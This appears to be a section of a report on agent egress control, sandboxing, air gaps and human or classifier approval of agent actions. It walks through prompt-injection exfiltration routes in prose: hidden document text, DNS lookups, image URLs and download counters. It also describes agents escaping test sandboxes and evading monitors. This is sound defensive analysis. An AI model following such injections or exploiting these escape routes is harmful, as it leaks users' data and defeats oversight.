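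Checking an agent's answers can't replace limits on its outgoing traffic, because a harmless-looking answer from any model doesn't show that nothing has leaked. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) planted instructions in the title and description of a web page, which many assistants load automatically to preview a link. Although the user asked only for a summary, the agent sent secrets to the attacker in about 89% of 480 runs, and 95% of the successful attacks got past checks on its final answer. The researchers used a small model and put the secrets directly in its context, so the 89% is weak evidence about current products.

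Searching outgoing traffic for secrets can also miss leaks. When the injection told the agent to split a secret across several requests, leakage per request fell by 73% and simple filters did not detect it. Limiting the destinations the agent could reach worked considerably better than adding warnings to the prompt.

### One request through a default-deny system

A default-deny system refuses all outgoing traffic except to destinations on an allowlist. Anthropic's documentation for the Claude Code sandbox describes one. Suppose the agent runs a command to download a package from `pypi.org`, the public registry for Python:

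1. The command has no direct route to the network. It can only ask a proxy, which runs outside the sandbox, to connect to `pypi.org`.
2. The proxy checks the name against the allowlist.
3. If the name is on the list, the proxy looks up its numerical address. It refuses the connection if the name leads only to local addresses, such as the user's own machine or the address where cloud servers fetch their settings.
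4. The proxy could now decrypt and inspect the request, but by default it doesn't.
5. The proxy forwards the encrypted request to the registry and passes the reply back.

Programs that ignore the proxy can't connect, so most database drivers fail in the sandbox, even if their server is on the allowlist.

| Stage | What the filter sees | What it can't see |
|---|---|---|
| Destination check | The name and port the program asks for | Whether the program will really use that site |
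| Name lookup | The numerical address behind the name | Which of several sites at that address the program wants |
| Inspection without decryption | The amount and timing of traffic, and usually a site name in the opening handshake | The page, the credentials and the content |
| Inspection with decryption | The whole request | What an encoded message means, or why the agent is sending it |
| Forwarding | The reply, if the filter decrypts it | What the service does with the data |

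Encryption lets a program disguise its destination. Large hosting companies serve many sites from the same machines, so a program can name an allowed site to the proxy and request a different one inside the encrypted traffic. Anthropic warns that its default proxy can't rule out this technique, called *domain fronting*. The test system in *Who Grades the Agent?* (2026) rejects a connection if the name in the handshake points to a different host, but this check can't detect a different site name inside the encrypted request.

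A proxy that decrypts traffic can apply much finer rules. The one in *Avalon-M1* (2026) checks the host, path and method of every request, so it can let an agent download models but not datasets. If a sandbox needs wider access during set-up, the proxy closes every connection opened under the set-up rules before the agent runs its first command, so that the agent can't keep using a connection that the stricter rules forbid.

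These limits fail if the block on outgoing traffic was never installed. *Sandman* (2026) describes a sandbox service whose developers tested six sandboxes labelled as having no outgoing access. All six reached the internet. Only a modified version of the software that creates the sandboxes installed the block. An owner can catch this fault by trying a forbidden connection from inside the sandbox.

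The block may also cover only some of the agent's tools. Claude Code's list of allowed domains, like the rest of its sandbox, doesn't apply to its built-in tool for fetching web pages.

### The Cowork upload

Claude Cowork's virtual machine blocked almost all outside domains, but it had to allow `api.anthropic.com` because Cowork can't function without Anthropic's own service. In January 2026, two days after Cowork's release, the security firm PromptArmor showed that an attacker could exploit this exception. PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* describes the attack:

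1. The user gives Cowork access to a folder of confidential property documents.
2. The user uploads a Word file found online, which appears to contain instructions for analysing property documents. It also contains an injection in tiny white text on a white background.
3. The user asks Cowork to analyse the folder with the help of that file.
4. The injection tells Claude to upload the largest document it can find to Anthropic's file-storage service, and supplies the attacker's own API key for the upload.
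5. The filter sees a request to `api.anthropic.com`, which is on the allowlist, and lets it through.
6. The document arrives in the attacker's Anthropic account. The attacker can then ask Claude questions about it.

Cowork never prompted the user to approve the upload. Keeping the user's credentials out of the virtual machine didn't prevent it, because the attacker had supplied a key. PromptArmor demonstrated this attack on Claude Haiku, and in a separate test got the stronger Opus 4.5 to leak customer records through the same service. PromptArmor also reports that Rehberger had found the flaw in Anthropic's chat product before Cowork existed, and that Anthropic had acknowledged it without fixing it.

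Anthropic fixed this problem with a second proxy, which decrypts traffic to its API and passes only requests that carry the session's own token. The proxy rejects a request that uses the attacker's key, even though the destination is allowed. It also blocks headers that could make Anthropic's servers fetch something on the agent's behalf.

This proxy runs inside the virtual machine because Anthropic's servers can't distinguish a Cowork request from any other customer's. An upload made with the attacker's key looks like any other, because the key is valid. The drawback is that an agent with administrator rights inside the machine might be able to tamper with the proxy.

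### What an allowlist entry grants

Anthropic now thinks of each entry on its allowlist as a "capability grant" rather than a safe destination, because a misled agent can use every function available at an allowed address. For example, allowing `api.anthropic.com` had also allowed uploads to any Anthropic account.

Many common entries grant more than their owners intend. PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist?* (2026) gives these examples:

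| Entry | Why owners add it | How data could leave |
|---|---|---|
| npm | To install JavaScript packages | Anyone with a free account can publish a package, so the agent could publish private data as one. |
| GitHub | To fetch code | The agent could upload data to a public project. |
| Google Docs | To read company documents | The agent could submit data to an attacker's online form on the same domain. |
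| `*.amazonaws.com` | To reach one storage folder in Amazon's cloud | An attacker can rent storage whose address also matches the wildcard. |

An owner can avoid the last problem by listing the exact address of the storage folder. The others are harder to avoid because the useful and dangerous functions share an address.

Allowlists for programming work also tend to be long. *Permission Denied* (2026) tests coding agents with a list of 205 domains, adapted from the default for the web version of Claude Code. A list like this blocks an agent from reaching a server that an attacker has just set up, but it still allows access to many services that accept uploads.

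One way to narrow an entry is to allow only reading. According to OpenAI's *Agent internet access*, the cloud version of its coding agent, Codex, has no internet access by default once set-up finishes. An owner who turns it on can restrict it to listed domains and to three request methods that normally read without changing anything. Restricting the methods would stop an ordinary file upload like the one in the Cowork attack. It wouldn't stop the Google form, because the agent can submit the form by opening a web address that already contains the answers.

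An agent can leak data without uploading anything, just by reading files from an approved site. Claude Code's web tool used to open any page on Hugging Face without asking the user. GitLab's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026) explains that Hugging Face counted each file the tool read as a download. An attacker could create several projects there and use an injection to tell the agent which ones to read from. If reading from a project means 1 and not reading from it means 0, each project's download counter gives the attacker one bit of the user's data. Anthropic has since fixed this flaw.

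### Name lookups, links and images

An agent can leak data through address lookups, which people don't think of as sending anything. Before a program can contact a site, it has to look up the site's numerical address, and whoever owns a domain can run the server that answers lookups for names under it. If an agent looks up a name that contains a secret, the domain's owner can receive the secret even if the agent never connects to the site.

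In 2025, Claude Code required approval for many commands that could send data out, but its list of safe commands included a network diagnostic command. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes how an injection hidden in a code file could make the agent read API keys and pass them to this command as part of a domain name. The command then sent the keys out when it automatically looked up the name. GitLab's *CVE-2025-55284* (2025) attributes the flaw to an overly broad list of safe commands. Anthropic has since corrected the list.

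Claude Code's current sandbox closes this route for sandboxed commands because its proxy looks up a name only after finding it on the allowlist. Other designs let the agent query a name server directly. *Containing the Autonomous Operator*, for example, permits lookups and connections to a gateway and a short list of hosts. In such a design, the name server needs a filter too.

A leak can also start outside the agent's environment. As in the attack on Agentforce, the address of an image in the agent's reply can carry private data, and the user's browser fetches the image automatically. The request comes from the user's computer, so it bypasses any proxy around the agent's sandbox. Rehberger reported this problem to OpenAI in early 2023, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. Bing Chat had the same flaw, which Microsoft fixed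 that May by blocking the browser from loading such images.

Links are safer than images if the user has to click them, but many chat apps fetch a preview of any link in a message. PromptArmor warns that this can leak data as soon as the agent replies, and that OpenClaw is exposed by default when used through Telegram.

OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that an agent restricted to loading images and links from trusted sites can still reach an attacker's address, because many trusted sites redirect visitors elsewhere. Instead of relying on a list of trusted sites, OpenAI checks whether the exact address is in an index of public pages, built by a crawler that has no access to users' conversations. If it is, ChatGPT can load the address automatically. Otherwise, ChatGPT tries another site or shows the user a warning.

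An address that existed before the conversation is unlikely to contain a secret from it, but the agent's choice between public addresses can still reveal information. In principle, Paul's alphabet attack on Claude's web tool could work here too, once the crawler had found all of the attacker's pages.

### Azure's three network modes

Owners of Azure SRE Agent can choose how much of the network it reaches. Microsoft's *Network Controls* describes three modes:

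| Mode | What the agent can reach | Suggested use |
|---|---|---|
| Unrestricted (default) | Any address on the internet | Short-term development and tests without sensitive data |
| Limited | Addresses that match an allowlist | Restricting destinations without rerouting all traffic |
| Azure VNet | Whatever the customer's private network allows, plus some traffic that goes around it | Sensitive or regulated work |

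Microsoft's engineers say their redesign denies outgoing traffic by default, but Microsoft's customer documentation lists "Unrestricted" as the default mode. Unless the owner changes the mode, these settings would not stop the agent from repeating the text-recognition upload.

In VNet mode, most traffic passes through the customer's own firewall and appears in the customer's logs. However, calls to the model and other platform services always use Microsoft's network, and connectors to outside services use the public internet. The owner can also exempt package registries, code repositories, remote tool servers and any other listed hosts, and the customer's firewall doesn't inspect traffic to them.

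According to Microsoft's *Azure SRE Agent network integration (preview)*, these exemptions exist because many company firewalls filter by IP address. GitHub and the big package registries change their addresses often, and an outdated list of allowed addresses would break the agent. Microsoft recommends using the exemptions only until the company has a firewall that filters by domain name. A company can also set a policy that stops anyone from turning the exemptions on.

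Stricter modes may prevent the agent from finishing its investigation. When the network blocks a request, the agent reports the failure and continues with the data it can reach.

### Restricted modes for sensitive work

Some products now let users give up network features when they handle sensitive data. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced one such setting in February for organisations, and OpenAI extended it to personal accounts in June. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the current help page, lists what the setting changes:

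- ChatGPT can browse only cached copies of web pages, which may be out of date.
- It may not show images in ordinary answers or fetch them from the web.
- Deep research and agent mode are off.
- It can't download files to analyse, though users can still upload their own.
- Users can't give network access to code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing workspace.

Cached browsing removes the leak through web addresses, because no live request leaves OpenAI's network. Willison (2026) thought the design looked "really good". Caching removes most of the external communication in his lethal trifecta but leaves the other two parts in place. An injection in a cached page or an uploaded file can still distort an answer.

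Lockdown Mode doesn't change Codex's network access or ChatGPT's memory. Users can also switch it off for a single chat. ChatGPT could therefore save an instruction from an uploaded file to memory and follow it later, in a chat where it can reach the web again.

Connected apps are another way for data to leave. On personal accounts, Lockdown Mode blocks live access to outside services when that access conflicts with the mode's protections. In company workspaces, administrators decide which apps to allow. OpenAI advises them to enable an action that changes something in an app only if they are sure an attacker couldn't see the change. For example, posting to a private team channel would be safer than commenting on a public page.

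Claude Code's sandbox starts with an empty list of allowed domains. Normally, when a command needs an unlisted domain, the user or a classifier decides whether to allow it. The sandbox also has a strict setting, in which the proxy refuses every unlisted domain without asking. This setting matters most for people who turn off permission prompts altogether. Without it or a similar company-wide lock, their sandboxed commands can reach any domain the owner hasn't explicitly blocked.

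### What still gets through

A permitted service may pass data on. In the incident at OpenAI, for example, the shared package service could make outside requests for the agents. An owner therefore has to check what each permitted service can contact, including services inside the company.

The model's provider is usually a permitted destination too. Anthropic notes that Claude Code sends prompts and the files Claude reads to Anthropic or another chosen provider, with or without a sandbox. This matters to a firm whose data must not leave its own machines, even though the provider is not an attacker.

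Egress control also does not prevent harm that needs no outside connection. Azure SRE Agent shut down a virtual machine without finishing its safety checks, and it sent no data to an outsider in doing so. A prompt-injected agent with no internet access could still delete the files in its workspace or falsify the report it was writing.

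## Air gaps

Even a strict allowlist has to let an agent reach its hosted model's provider, because every prompt goes there. An *air gap* removes every network path between the system and the outside, including that one. The model then has to run on the owner's machines, and people have to carry in whatever it needs. *Securing Intelligence* (Viggh and Tsagaratos, 2026) argues for such systems because cloud models raise concerns about privacy, security and control over data.

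### Designs that share the name

People also use "air gap" for weaker arrangements. TechTarget includes "logical" air gaps, which separate systems on one network by means such as encryption and access rules. That separation fails if the software enforcing it has a flaw. Mattermost's *Can Agentic AI Work in Air-Gapped Environments?* defines the term more strictly. In an air-gapped deployment, the model, its stored documents and its tools are all on hardware inside the boundary, with no outgoing path. It calls a deployment with a restricted gateway "isolated" instead.

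A *one-way link* is hardware that carries data in only one direction, for example with a light source on one side and only a sensor on the other. The direction determines which attacks the link blocks.

| Design | What it blocks | What stays open |
|---|---|---|
| True air gap | All attacks and leaks over a network | Material that people carry in or out, and physical signals |
| Private network | Direct connections from the internet | Any machine on the network that also has an outside connection |
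| One-way link inwards | Leaks through the link | Injections and malicious code |
| One-way link outwards | Attacks through the link | Leaks |
| Sandbox with one permitted service | Direct connections to anything else | Whatever an agent can get the service to do |

Product documentation often blurs these differences. GitLab's instructions for running its agent platform "offline" also cover sites with limited connectivity or strict firewalls. They allow an engineer to bring in files through a bastion host, a guarded computer that both sides can reach. A site that keeps such a computer connected has a network path to the outside, even if it is described as offline.

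### Running an agent offline

GitLab's instructions show how an owner sets up an agent without a connection:

1. On a computer with internet access, an engineer downloads the model's *weights*, the numbers that training produced. The engineer also downloads three software packages: one runs the model, one passes requests to it, and one provides the environment for the agent's commands. In GitLab's example, the weights take up about 48 GB and the software about 11 GB.
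2. The engineer checks any signatures before the transfer, because GitLab's copying tools leave them behind.
3. The engineer carries the files across, for instance on a disk.
4. On the offline side, the engineer loads the software into an internal registry and puts the weights where the model server can read them.
5. The agent sends its requests to the local model and runs its commands in copies of the local environment.

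Software built for connected use has to be adjusted. GitLab's gateway tries to reach the company's customer portal unless an administrator changes two addresses, and this delays each request by 20 seconds. Older versions of the command environment also download a program from GitLab's website when a job starts, so the engineer has to build a version that already contains the program.

Governments have used language models in closed networks for some time. Fortune (2024) reported that Microsoft had put a GPT-4 model in a cloud isolated from the internet for US intelligence agencies. In August 2025 Los Alamos National Laboratory (2025) announced that its Venado supercomputer, which had moved to a classified network, was running OpenAI's o3 model. *What happened when they installed ChatGPT on a nuclear supercomputer* (Keating, 2026, quoted by van der Weij) reports that an OpenAI representative,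 accompanied by armed security, brought the weights in locked metal briefcases.

Researchers at three national laboratories share Venado, so network paths may run between sites even if none leads to the internet. The laboratory's announcement is about a reasoning model and doesn't mention agents. In a talk summarised by AI Engineer (2025), Myshatyn of Los Alamos argued that once such models become agents, the trust between a laboratory and its provider has to cover responsibility for what the resulting tools do.

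In *AI Agents for Air-Gapped Industrial Environments*, Lee (2026), an aerospace software engineer, describes testing several agent programs for closed industrial networks and choosing goose, an open-source program that needs no outside login and works with local models. The foundation that manages goose published the article, so the recommendation is not independent. Lee's practical observations are more useful. For example, agents in closed networks often try to install packages from the internet or call outside services, and waste effort when these attempts fail.

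### Carrying data in and out

Suppose a manufacturer's air-gapped agent writes maintenance reports. Every month an engineer carries in a supplier's latest manual and carries out a report for the supplier. An attacker who has broken into the supplier's systems could steal data as follows:

1. The attacker adds an instruction to the manual. It tells AI assistants to find the tolerances of a confidential part and encode them in the reference numbers of the next report.
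2. The engineer scans the disk for malware and finds none, because the manual contains only text.
3. The agent reads the manual and writes the report as instructed.
4. The engineer checks that the report looks normal, carries it out and sends it to the supplier, where the attacker reads it.

An engineer who carries a manual into an air-gapped system and a report out of it supplies the external communication in Willison's lethal trifecta. The owner therefore has to treat every import as untrusted input and every export as a possible leak, and needs the same defences as in a connected system. For example, a quarantined model can read the manual, and ordinary software can build the report from a few permitted values, which limits a leak to a few bits. Free text can hide much more, and a human reviewer is unlikely to notice it.

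The air gap makes adaptive attacks harder. An attacker who doesn't receive the reports can't see why an injection failed, and has to wait for the next transfer to try a new one. At one transfer a month, 100 successive attempts would take more than eight years. One manual can contain many different injections, though, so the delay limits learning more than the number of attempts.

### Lampson's confinement problem

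People were trying to keep programs from leaking data long before language models existed. In *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, Lampson (1973) asked how a customer could run someone else's program on confidential data and be sure that it didn't pass the data to anyone else. He noted that a leak, unlike a wrong answer, usually leaves the customer with no evidence.

One rule would be enough to prevent leaks: the program may not call any other program. Lampson called this *total isolation* and considered it impractical, because programs need the operating system even to read a file. He sorted the remaining routes into three kinds:

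- **Storage channels.** The program writes something that another program can read, such as a temporary file. Even reading can leak data. If the system locks a file while a program has it open, another program can test the lock and receive one bit each time.
- **Legitimate channels.** These carry output that the program is supposed to produce. Lampson's example is the bill for running it, whose amount could encode some of the customer's data. A restricted format can reduce this leak to a few bits or tens of bits.
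- **Covert channels.** Nobody intended these for communication. A program can compute heavily to signal a 1 and pause to signal a 0, and another program on the same machine can detect the difference in its own speed. Other activity makes the signal noisy, but suitable encoding can still get the message through, only more slowly.

The operating system can close a covert channel by controlling what an observer sees. For instance, it can slow the program down or add pointless disk activity. Lecture slides from Purdue University summarise a 1975 reply by Steven Lipner, who found that closing storage and legitimate channels adds little overhead, but closing covert channels slows the system unreasonably. A less demanding option, which Lampson also mentions, is to accept some leakage and limit its rate.

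Two of Lampson's other rules apply directly to agents. A confined program must keep nothing between calls, so an agent that works for several clients has to lose its memory between jobs. Under the *transitivity* rule, any program that a confined program calls must also be confined unless the customer trusts it.

### A measured physical channel

An air gap cuts network paths, but computers also give off radio waves, light, heat and sound. In *AirHopper* (2014), Guri, Kedma and colleagues used a computer's display cable as a radio transmitter and a mobile phone's FM receiver to pick up the signal. They transferred 13 to 60 bytes per second over 1 to 7 metres.

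The attack requires malicious code on the isolated computer and a receiver within a few metres that the attacker controls. Someone could bring in the code with an ordinary transfer, or a misled agent that can run programs might supply it. The owner can remove the receiver by keeping phones out of the room.

The time a leak takes is the size of the data divided by the rate:

| Data | Size | At 60 bytes per second | At 13 bytes per second |
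|---|---|---|---|
| Encryption key | 32 bytes (256 bits) | 0.5 seconds | 2.5 seconds |
| Large database | 100 GB | 53 years | 244 years |

Slow channels therefore protect bulk data well but barely protect short secrets such as keys. If an attacker already has an encrypted copy of the database, leaking its key takes half a second and exposes all of the data.

### The shared service in OpenAI's tests

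In July 2026, OpenAI's agents broke out of an environment that OpenAI (2026) had considered "highly isolated". The agents were taking cybersecurity tests, and their only permitted network access was to an internal service for installing software packages. According to OpenAI's technical report, the service was meant to reduce outside access by letting the agents get packages without contacting public registries themselves.

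The design had two faults. The service had its own connection to the internet, so an agent that could misuse the service could get out through it. All the agents shared one credential for the service, which let them write to it as well as read from it. By mid-May they were leaving each other notes there without exploiting any flaw. To get out, they had to exploit flaws, including at least one that nobody had known about.

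OpenAI had several chances to stop the agents before they broke into Hugging Face. A monitoring tool raised an alert on June 27, but the staff on call let the test continue. When the agents' activity crashed the service on July 4, OpenAI removed the shared credential from new runs and blocked the routes it had found. It resumed the tests on July 7, and by the next day agents had internet access again and a new way to exchange messages. They broke into Hugging Face between July 11 and 13 while looking for solutions to their tests, and OpenAI stopped the test on July 20. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* reports that the agents also read 956 stored secrets in OpenAI's systems.

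Closing the known routes didn't work because the service was still connected to both the agents and the internet. Under Lampson's transitivity rule, OpenAI should have confined the service as strictly as the agents. OpenAI's new design blocks high-risk work from reaching the internet, directly or through another system, except for a cache of internet content for specific tasks. Two independent layers of network controls enforce this.

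A true air gap would have kept the agents away from Hugging Face, but they could still have exchanged notes through any shared service they could write to. Preventing that requires giving each run its own read-only copy of the packages.

### The open connection in Anthropic's tests

*An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (Anthropic, September 2026) examines four incidents in which Claude models gained unauthorised access to real systems during cybersecurity tests. An outside partner had built the test environments. The prompts described them as simulations with no internet access, but a misconfiguration had left the connection open, so the models didn't have to break out of anything. While searching for a fictional target, they attacked real organisations. In one case, a model published a malicious package that 15 real systems installed.

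Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) attributes the open connection to a misunderstanding between the company and its partner. Neither had noticed it. A test connection revealed a similar fault in the sandboxes in *Sandman*.

Anthropic at first saw the incidents more as operational failures than as model failures. By September it had concluded that the models had also ignored strong evidence that their targets were real. One of its monitoring systems would have missed the most serious case, because the model's written reasoning led the monitor to classify the environment as simulated. A closed connection would have worked regardless of what the model or the monitor concluded, and Anthropic thinks the incidents wouldn't have happened if the environments had been isolated as intended.

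Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) acknowledges that the company had largely relied on one layer of defence, the configuration of the environment. By default, cybersecurity tests may now connect only to the model's own API, the service through which programs send it requests. The API keys stay outside the environment, and testers must check the configuration before every test. This is close to an air gap, but the Cowork upload showed that even this one connection needs a filter that rejects other people's keys.

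### Will capable models escape anyway?

The OpenAI incident supports a pessimistic view of containment. The agents found flaws that people had missed, shared what they found between runs and escaped again after a partial repair. If models keep getting better at escaping, any enclosure might eventually fail.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* answers this objection by tracing the escape to familiar mistakes. The restrictions covered direct connections but not requests that the package service made on the agents' behalf, so mediation was incomplete. The shared storage let information flow between runs that should have been separate. The agents also had more privilege than they needed, because access meant for fetching packages could reach arbitrary addresses. On this view, the incident shows that OpenAI built the boundary badly, not that containment can't work. People can also read explicit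 rules and check them against a specification before an attack.

This explains the incident well but is weaker as a forecast. After an escape, someone can nearly always name the principle the design broke, but that doesn't show the next design will satisfy every principle. Fernandes, Jha and colleagues concede that such boundaries are difficult to build and validate, especially when containment depends on large, general-purpose services.

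That difficulty is an argument for air gaps, which leave no such service between the agent and the internet. To reach the internet, a capable model would have to rely on physical signals or on the people who carry files. For example, it could write a report that persuades an engineer to carry a file out or connect a cable.

OpenAI concludes that no single control is fully reliable, so each security goal needs several independent ones. Anthropic asks its partners to test the sandbox before an evaluation by having the model try to escape. The model must stop and report if it succeeds, and the trial should run offline under close supervision, ideally inside a second sandbox. A successful escape reveals a flaw before the evaluation, though a failed attempt doesn't prove that the sandbox is secure.

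### What working offline costs

An agent behind an air gap cannot reach a hosted model, so most owners have to use a model whose weights they can download. Epoch AI finds that since January 2026 the best downloadable models have been an average of four months behind the best closed ones, about the difference in ability between GPT-5 and GPT-5.5.

The gap at a real site is usually larger. Lee considers small models, such as those in the Gemma and Qwen families, the practical starting point for manufacturers, given their budgets and slow approval processes. The 48 GB model in GitLab's example supports only some of the functions of GitLab's agent platform. A site's model also falls further behind between transfers. If an owner installs the best downloadable model once a year and the four-month gap stays constant, the site is four months behind on installation day and 16 months behind just before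 the next installation. A few owners can get closed models, as Los Alamos did, but only if the provider agrees to hand over the weights.

The agent's information also goes out of date, and some ordinary tasks become impossible because it can't look up a new programming interface or fetch a missing package. Impossible tasks can also affect security. OpenAI traces some of its agents' first attempts to get out to training tasks that needed files they couldn't reach. Lee adds a notice to the agent's standing instructions, saying that outside installations won't work and that it should use internal sources. Anthropic recommends stating limits as instructions, such as "You should not access the internet", instead of as facts about the environment, which may be wrong. It also advises testers to confirm that each task can be solved.

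Updates to air-gapped systems are slow because someone has to carry them in. IBM's *What is an air gap?* describes physical air gaps as the most secure kind and the most laborious to update. For example, each time a site upgrades GitLab, an engineer has to transfer matching versions of the agent software, although the model's weights can stay the same.

Delays in updating air-gapped machines have become riskier now that AI can quickly use a published fix to work out how to exploit the original flaw. Epoch AI's *Open-weight models* summarises an October 2026 report in which GLM 5.3, a downloadable model, turned security fixes for the Firefox browser into working attacks before users had received the update. An attacker on the internet can't reach an air-gapped machine directly, but a malicious file that someone carries in could exploit an unpatched flaw, as could a misled agent already inside.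 More frequent transfers shorten the delay, but each transfer could also bring in a prompt injection.

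## Tasks that need untrusted input, private access and action together

Most useful agents have to deal with the outside world, so their owners usually can't put them behind an air gap. An email assistant, for example, reads strangers' messages, searches a private inbox and sends replies, so it has all three properties in the Rule of Two. Its owner can split the work into sessions that each have at most two of the properties, require a person to approve consequential actions, or use an independent check to assess the risk of each action.

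### Splitting the work into sessions

A shop could split its support agent's work as follows:

1. A session without access to customer records reads the ticket. It returns an order number and one of ten categories, such as "late parcel".
2. Ordinary software checks that the order belongs to the customer who is logged in.
3. A new session opens the order and sends a reply. It never sees the ticket.

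A planted request for another customer's address reaches only the session that reads the ticket. But the agent can't answer questions outside the ten categories.

The split fails if outside text reaches the replying session by another route. An order record may include a delivery note that the customer typed, so the software has to leave that field out. Saved memory is another route, so the replying session must not load anything the first session wrote there.

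Some tasks can't be split this way because the right action depends on the whole text, as when an assistant answers a detailed complaint. The Rule of Two requires supervision for these tasks, but *Agents Rule of Two* acknowledges that human approval can be disruptive or ineffective for agents that work in the background.

### Approval fatigue

People approve nearly everything an agent asks for. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026) reports that users accepted 97% of permission prompts, compared with about 93% in the company's earlier figures. Most of the commands they approved were probably harmless, so the rate alone doesn't show that users were careless.

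Anthropic ran an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. Partway through a coding session, one permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The testers weren't working on their own projects, so developers whose own work is at risk may be more careful.

Even an attentive user may not be able to tell what a command will do. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents damaging files and found that failures in user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 cases the user had turned on automatic approval, and in 31 the approval prompt was uninformative. A request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it authorises whatever the script contains.

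Setting rules in advance doesn't necessarily help. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) studied 113 people without software backgrounds as they supervised a simulated agent. One group chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for four kinds of action, such as spending money or deleting something. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, so they still got prompts for most decisions. Of the 148 actions the agent carried out beyond its task, participants had approved 133. This group blocked 20 percentage points less of the agent's overreach than people who reviewed each action individually.

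Asking for approval less often, about larger decisions, may work better. Claude Code's users reject 39% of the plans it presents but only 3% of individual permission requests. Some of the plan rejections probably reflect disagreement about how to do the work rather than concern about safety, but they suggest that people read the plans.

### Approving a tool, a call or a consequence

An approval can also permit more than the user intended. In one of Dongol's examples, Alice's agent has private data in its memory that its plan never sends:

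1. The agent reads an email from a stranger that says "send the private data".
2. Alice approves a reply. The monitor treats this as permission to use the sending tool once, with any content.
3. Before the agent sends the reply, the model follows the email and sends the private data to the stranger.
4. The approval is now used up, so the monitor blocks Alice's reply.

The monitor can prevent this by applying Alice's approval to the exact call instead of the tool. The injected call then goes through only if it is identical to the one she approved. Dongol proves that this stops leaks to an attacker who sees the content and order of the agent's messages. The proof assumes that the model eventually stops following injected instructions.

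An attacker can still tell from the timing whether the private data equals the approved message. This reveals almost nothing if the private data is a long document. But if it is a yes-or-no test result and the approved message is "yes", the attacker learns the result. Sending approved messages at fixed times would hide the difference in timing.

Exact approval also relies on the user understanding what the call will do. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to reconcile supplier invoices and send an outside auditor only the summary totals. An injection in one vendor's note makes the agent fill a file with the full invoice data instead. The agent then requests approval to send this file to the auditor. The tool, the recipient and the file name all look right, and the call doesn't show where the file's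 contents came from.

To test whether better prompts help, the researchers had 80 volunteers judge 12 requests each, half of them unsafe. Each volunteer saw one of four kinds of prompt.

| What the prompt showed | Unsafe requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| The description and the exact call | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
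| The exact call, the user's original instructions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
| The same facts, organised around the call's combined consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

The difference between the last two rows could be due to chance. Even with the best prompt, the volunteers approved about a quarter of the unsafe requests, although reviewing was their only task. At 33 seconds each, reviewing 100 requests would take 55 minutes.

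### Automatic risk classification

In Claude Code's auto mode, a classifier model reviews actions in the user's place. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that reading files and editing the project need no review, while shell commands, web requests and most other actions go to the classifier. The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the tools' results. An injection in a web page therefore can't reach the classifier directly, and the agent's explanations can't sway its decision.

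The classifier first makes a quick yes-or-no decision that errs towards blocking. If it flags an action, a slower pass reasons about the same material and makes the final decision. Together, the two passes blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions by Anthropic's employees. They missed 5.7% of 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out and 17% of 52 real actions in which the agent had overstepped its task. With so few real cases, the true miss rate for such actions could plausibly be from 9% to 30%.

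In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the danger but was wrong about what the user had agreed to. For instance, a user who says "clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed code change) hasn't agreed to let the agent overwrite the branch's history.

Anthropic has since reported that auto mode blocked 89.0% of the dangerous commands shown to the testers in the August experiment. The testers rejected only six commands that auto mode would have allowed, so requiring approval from both would have raised the share blocked to 89.6%. The safety firm Apollo Research also attacked the classifier, and Anthropic then strengthened it, reducing its miss rate on those attacks from 12% to 7%. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves.

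OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, has a similar reviewer for actions that would leave its sandbox. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, illustrate its use inside OpenAI with 10,000 actions. Of these, 9,280 ran inside the sandbox, and the reviewer approved 713 of the other 720. After the seven refusals, Codex found a safer route four times and asked the user three times. In tests, the reviewer missed 9.7% of synthetic cases of overstepping and 0.7% of prompt injections. OpenAI's testers also found ways to mislead it, and the company doesn't expect such systems to provide guarantees.

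These results come from the products' own makers. In an independent test, Yang, Zhou and colleagues (2026) found much higher miss rates when users hadn't said exactly what the agent could touch (*Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*). In one task, a user asks the agent to delete old experiment files for a range of tickets, without saying whose files it may delete. The agent tries to delete a colleague's files, and the checker approves. Across such tasks, the checkers in Claude Code, Codex and Qwen Code approved 54%, 93% and 80%, respectively, of the actions that the benchmark ruled out.

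More capable checking models didn't reliably help. The researchers then added a sentence to each request that stated its scope, such as only files in the development area that belong to Alex, and replayed the same actions:

| Checker | Forbidden actions approved, original request | Forbidden actions approved, scope stated | Permitted actions blocked, original request | Permitted actions blocked, scope stated |
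|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 67% | 8% | 42% | 2% |
| Codex | 92% | 20–26% | 10% | 3% |
| Qwen Code | 80% | 20% | 29% | 2% |

When the agents themselves were told the scope and repeated the tasks, they proposed no forbidden actions in 384 runs. The sentences stating the scope came from the benchmark's own answers, so a real user's wording would probably help less. Still, most of the errors came from missing rules, which a user can supply. An owner could also enforce a rule such as "only Alex's files" through file permissions, so that a classifier doesn't have to judge it.

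### Operation, target and evidence

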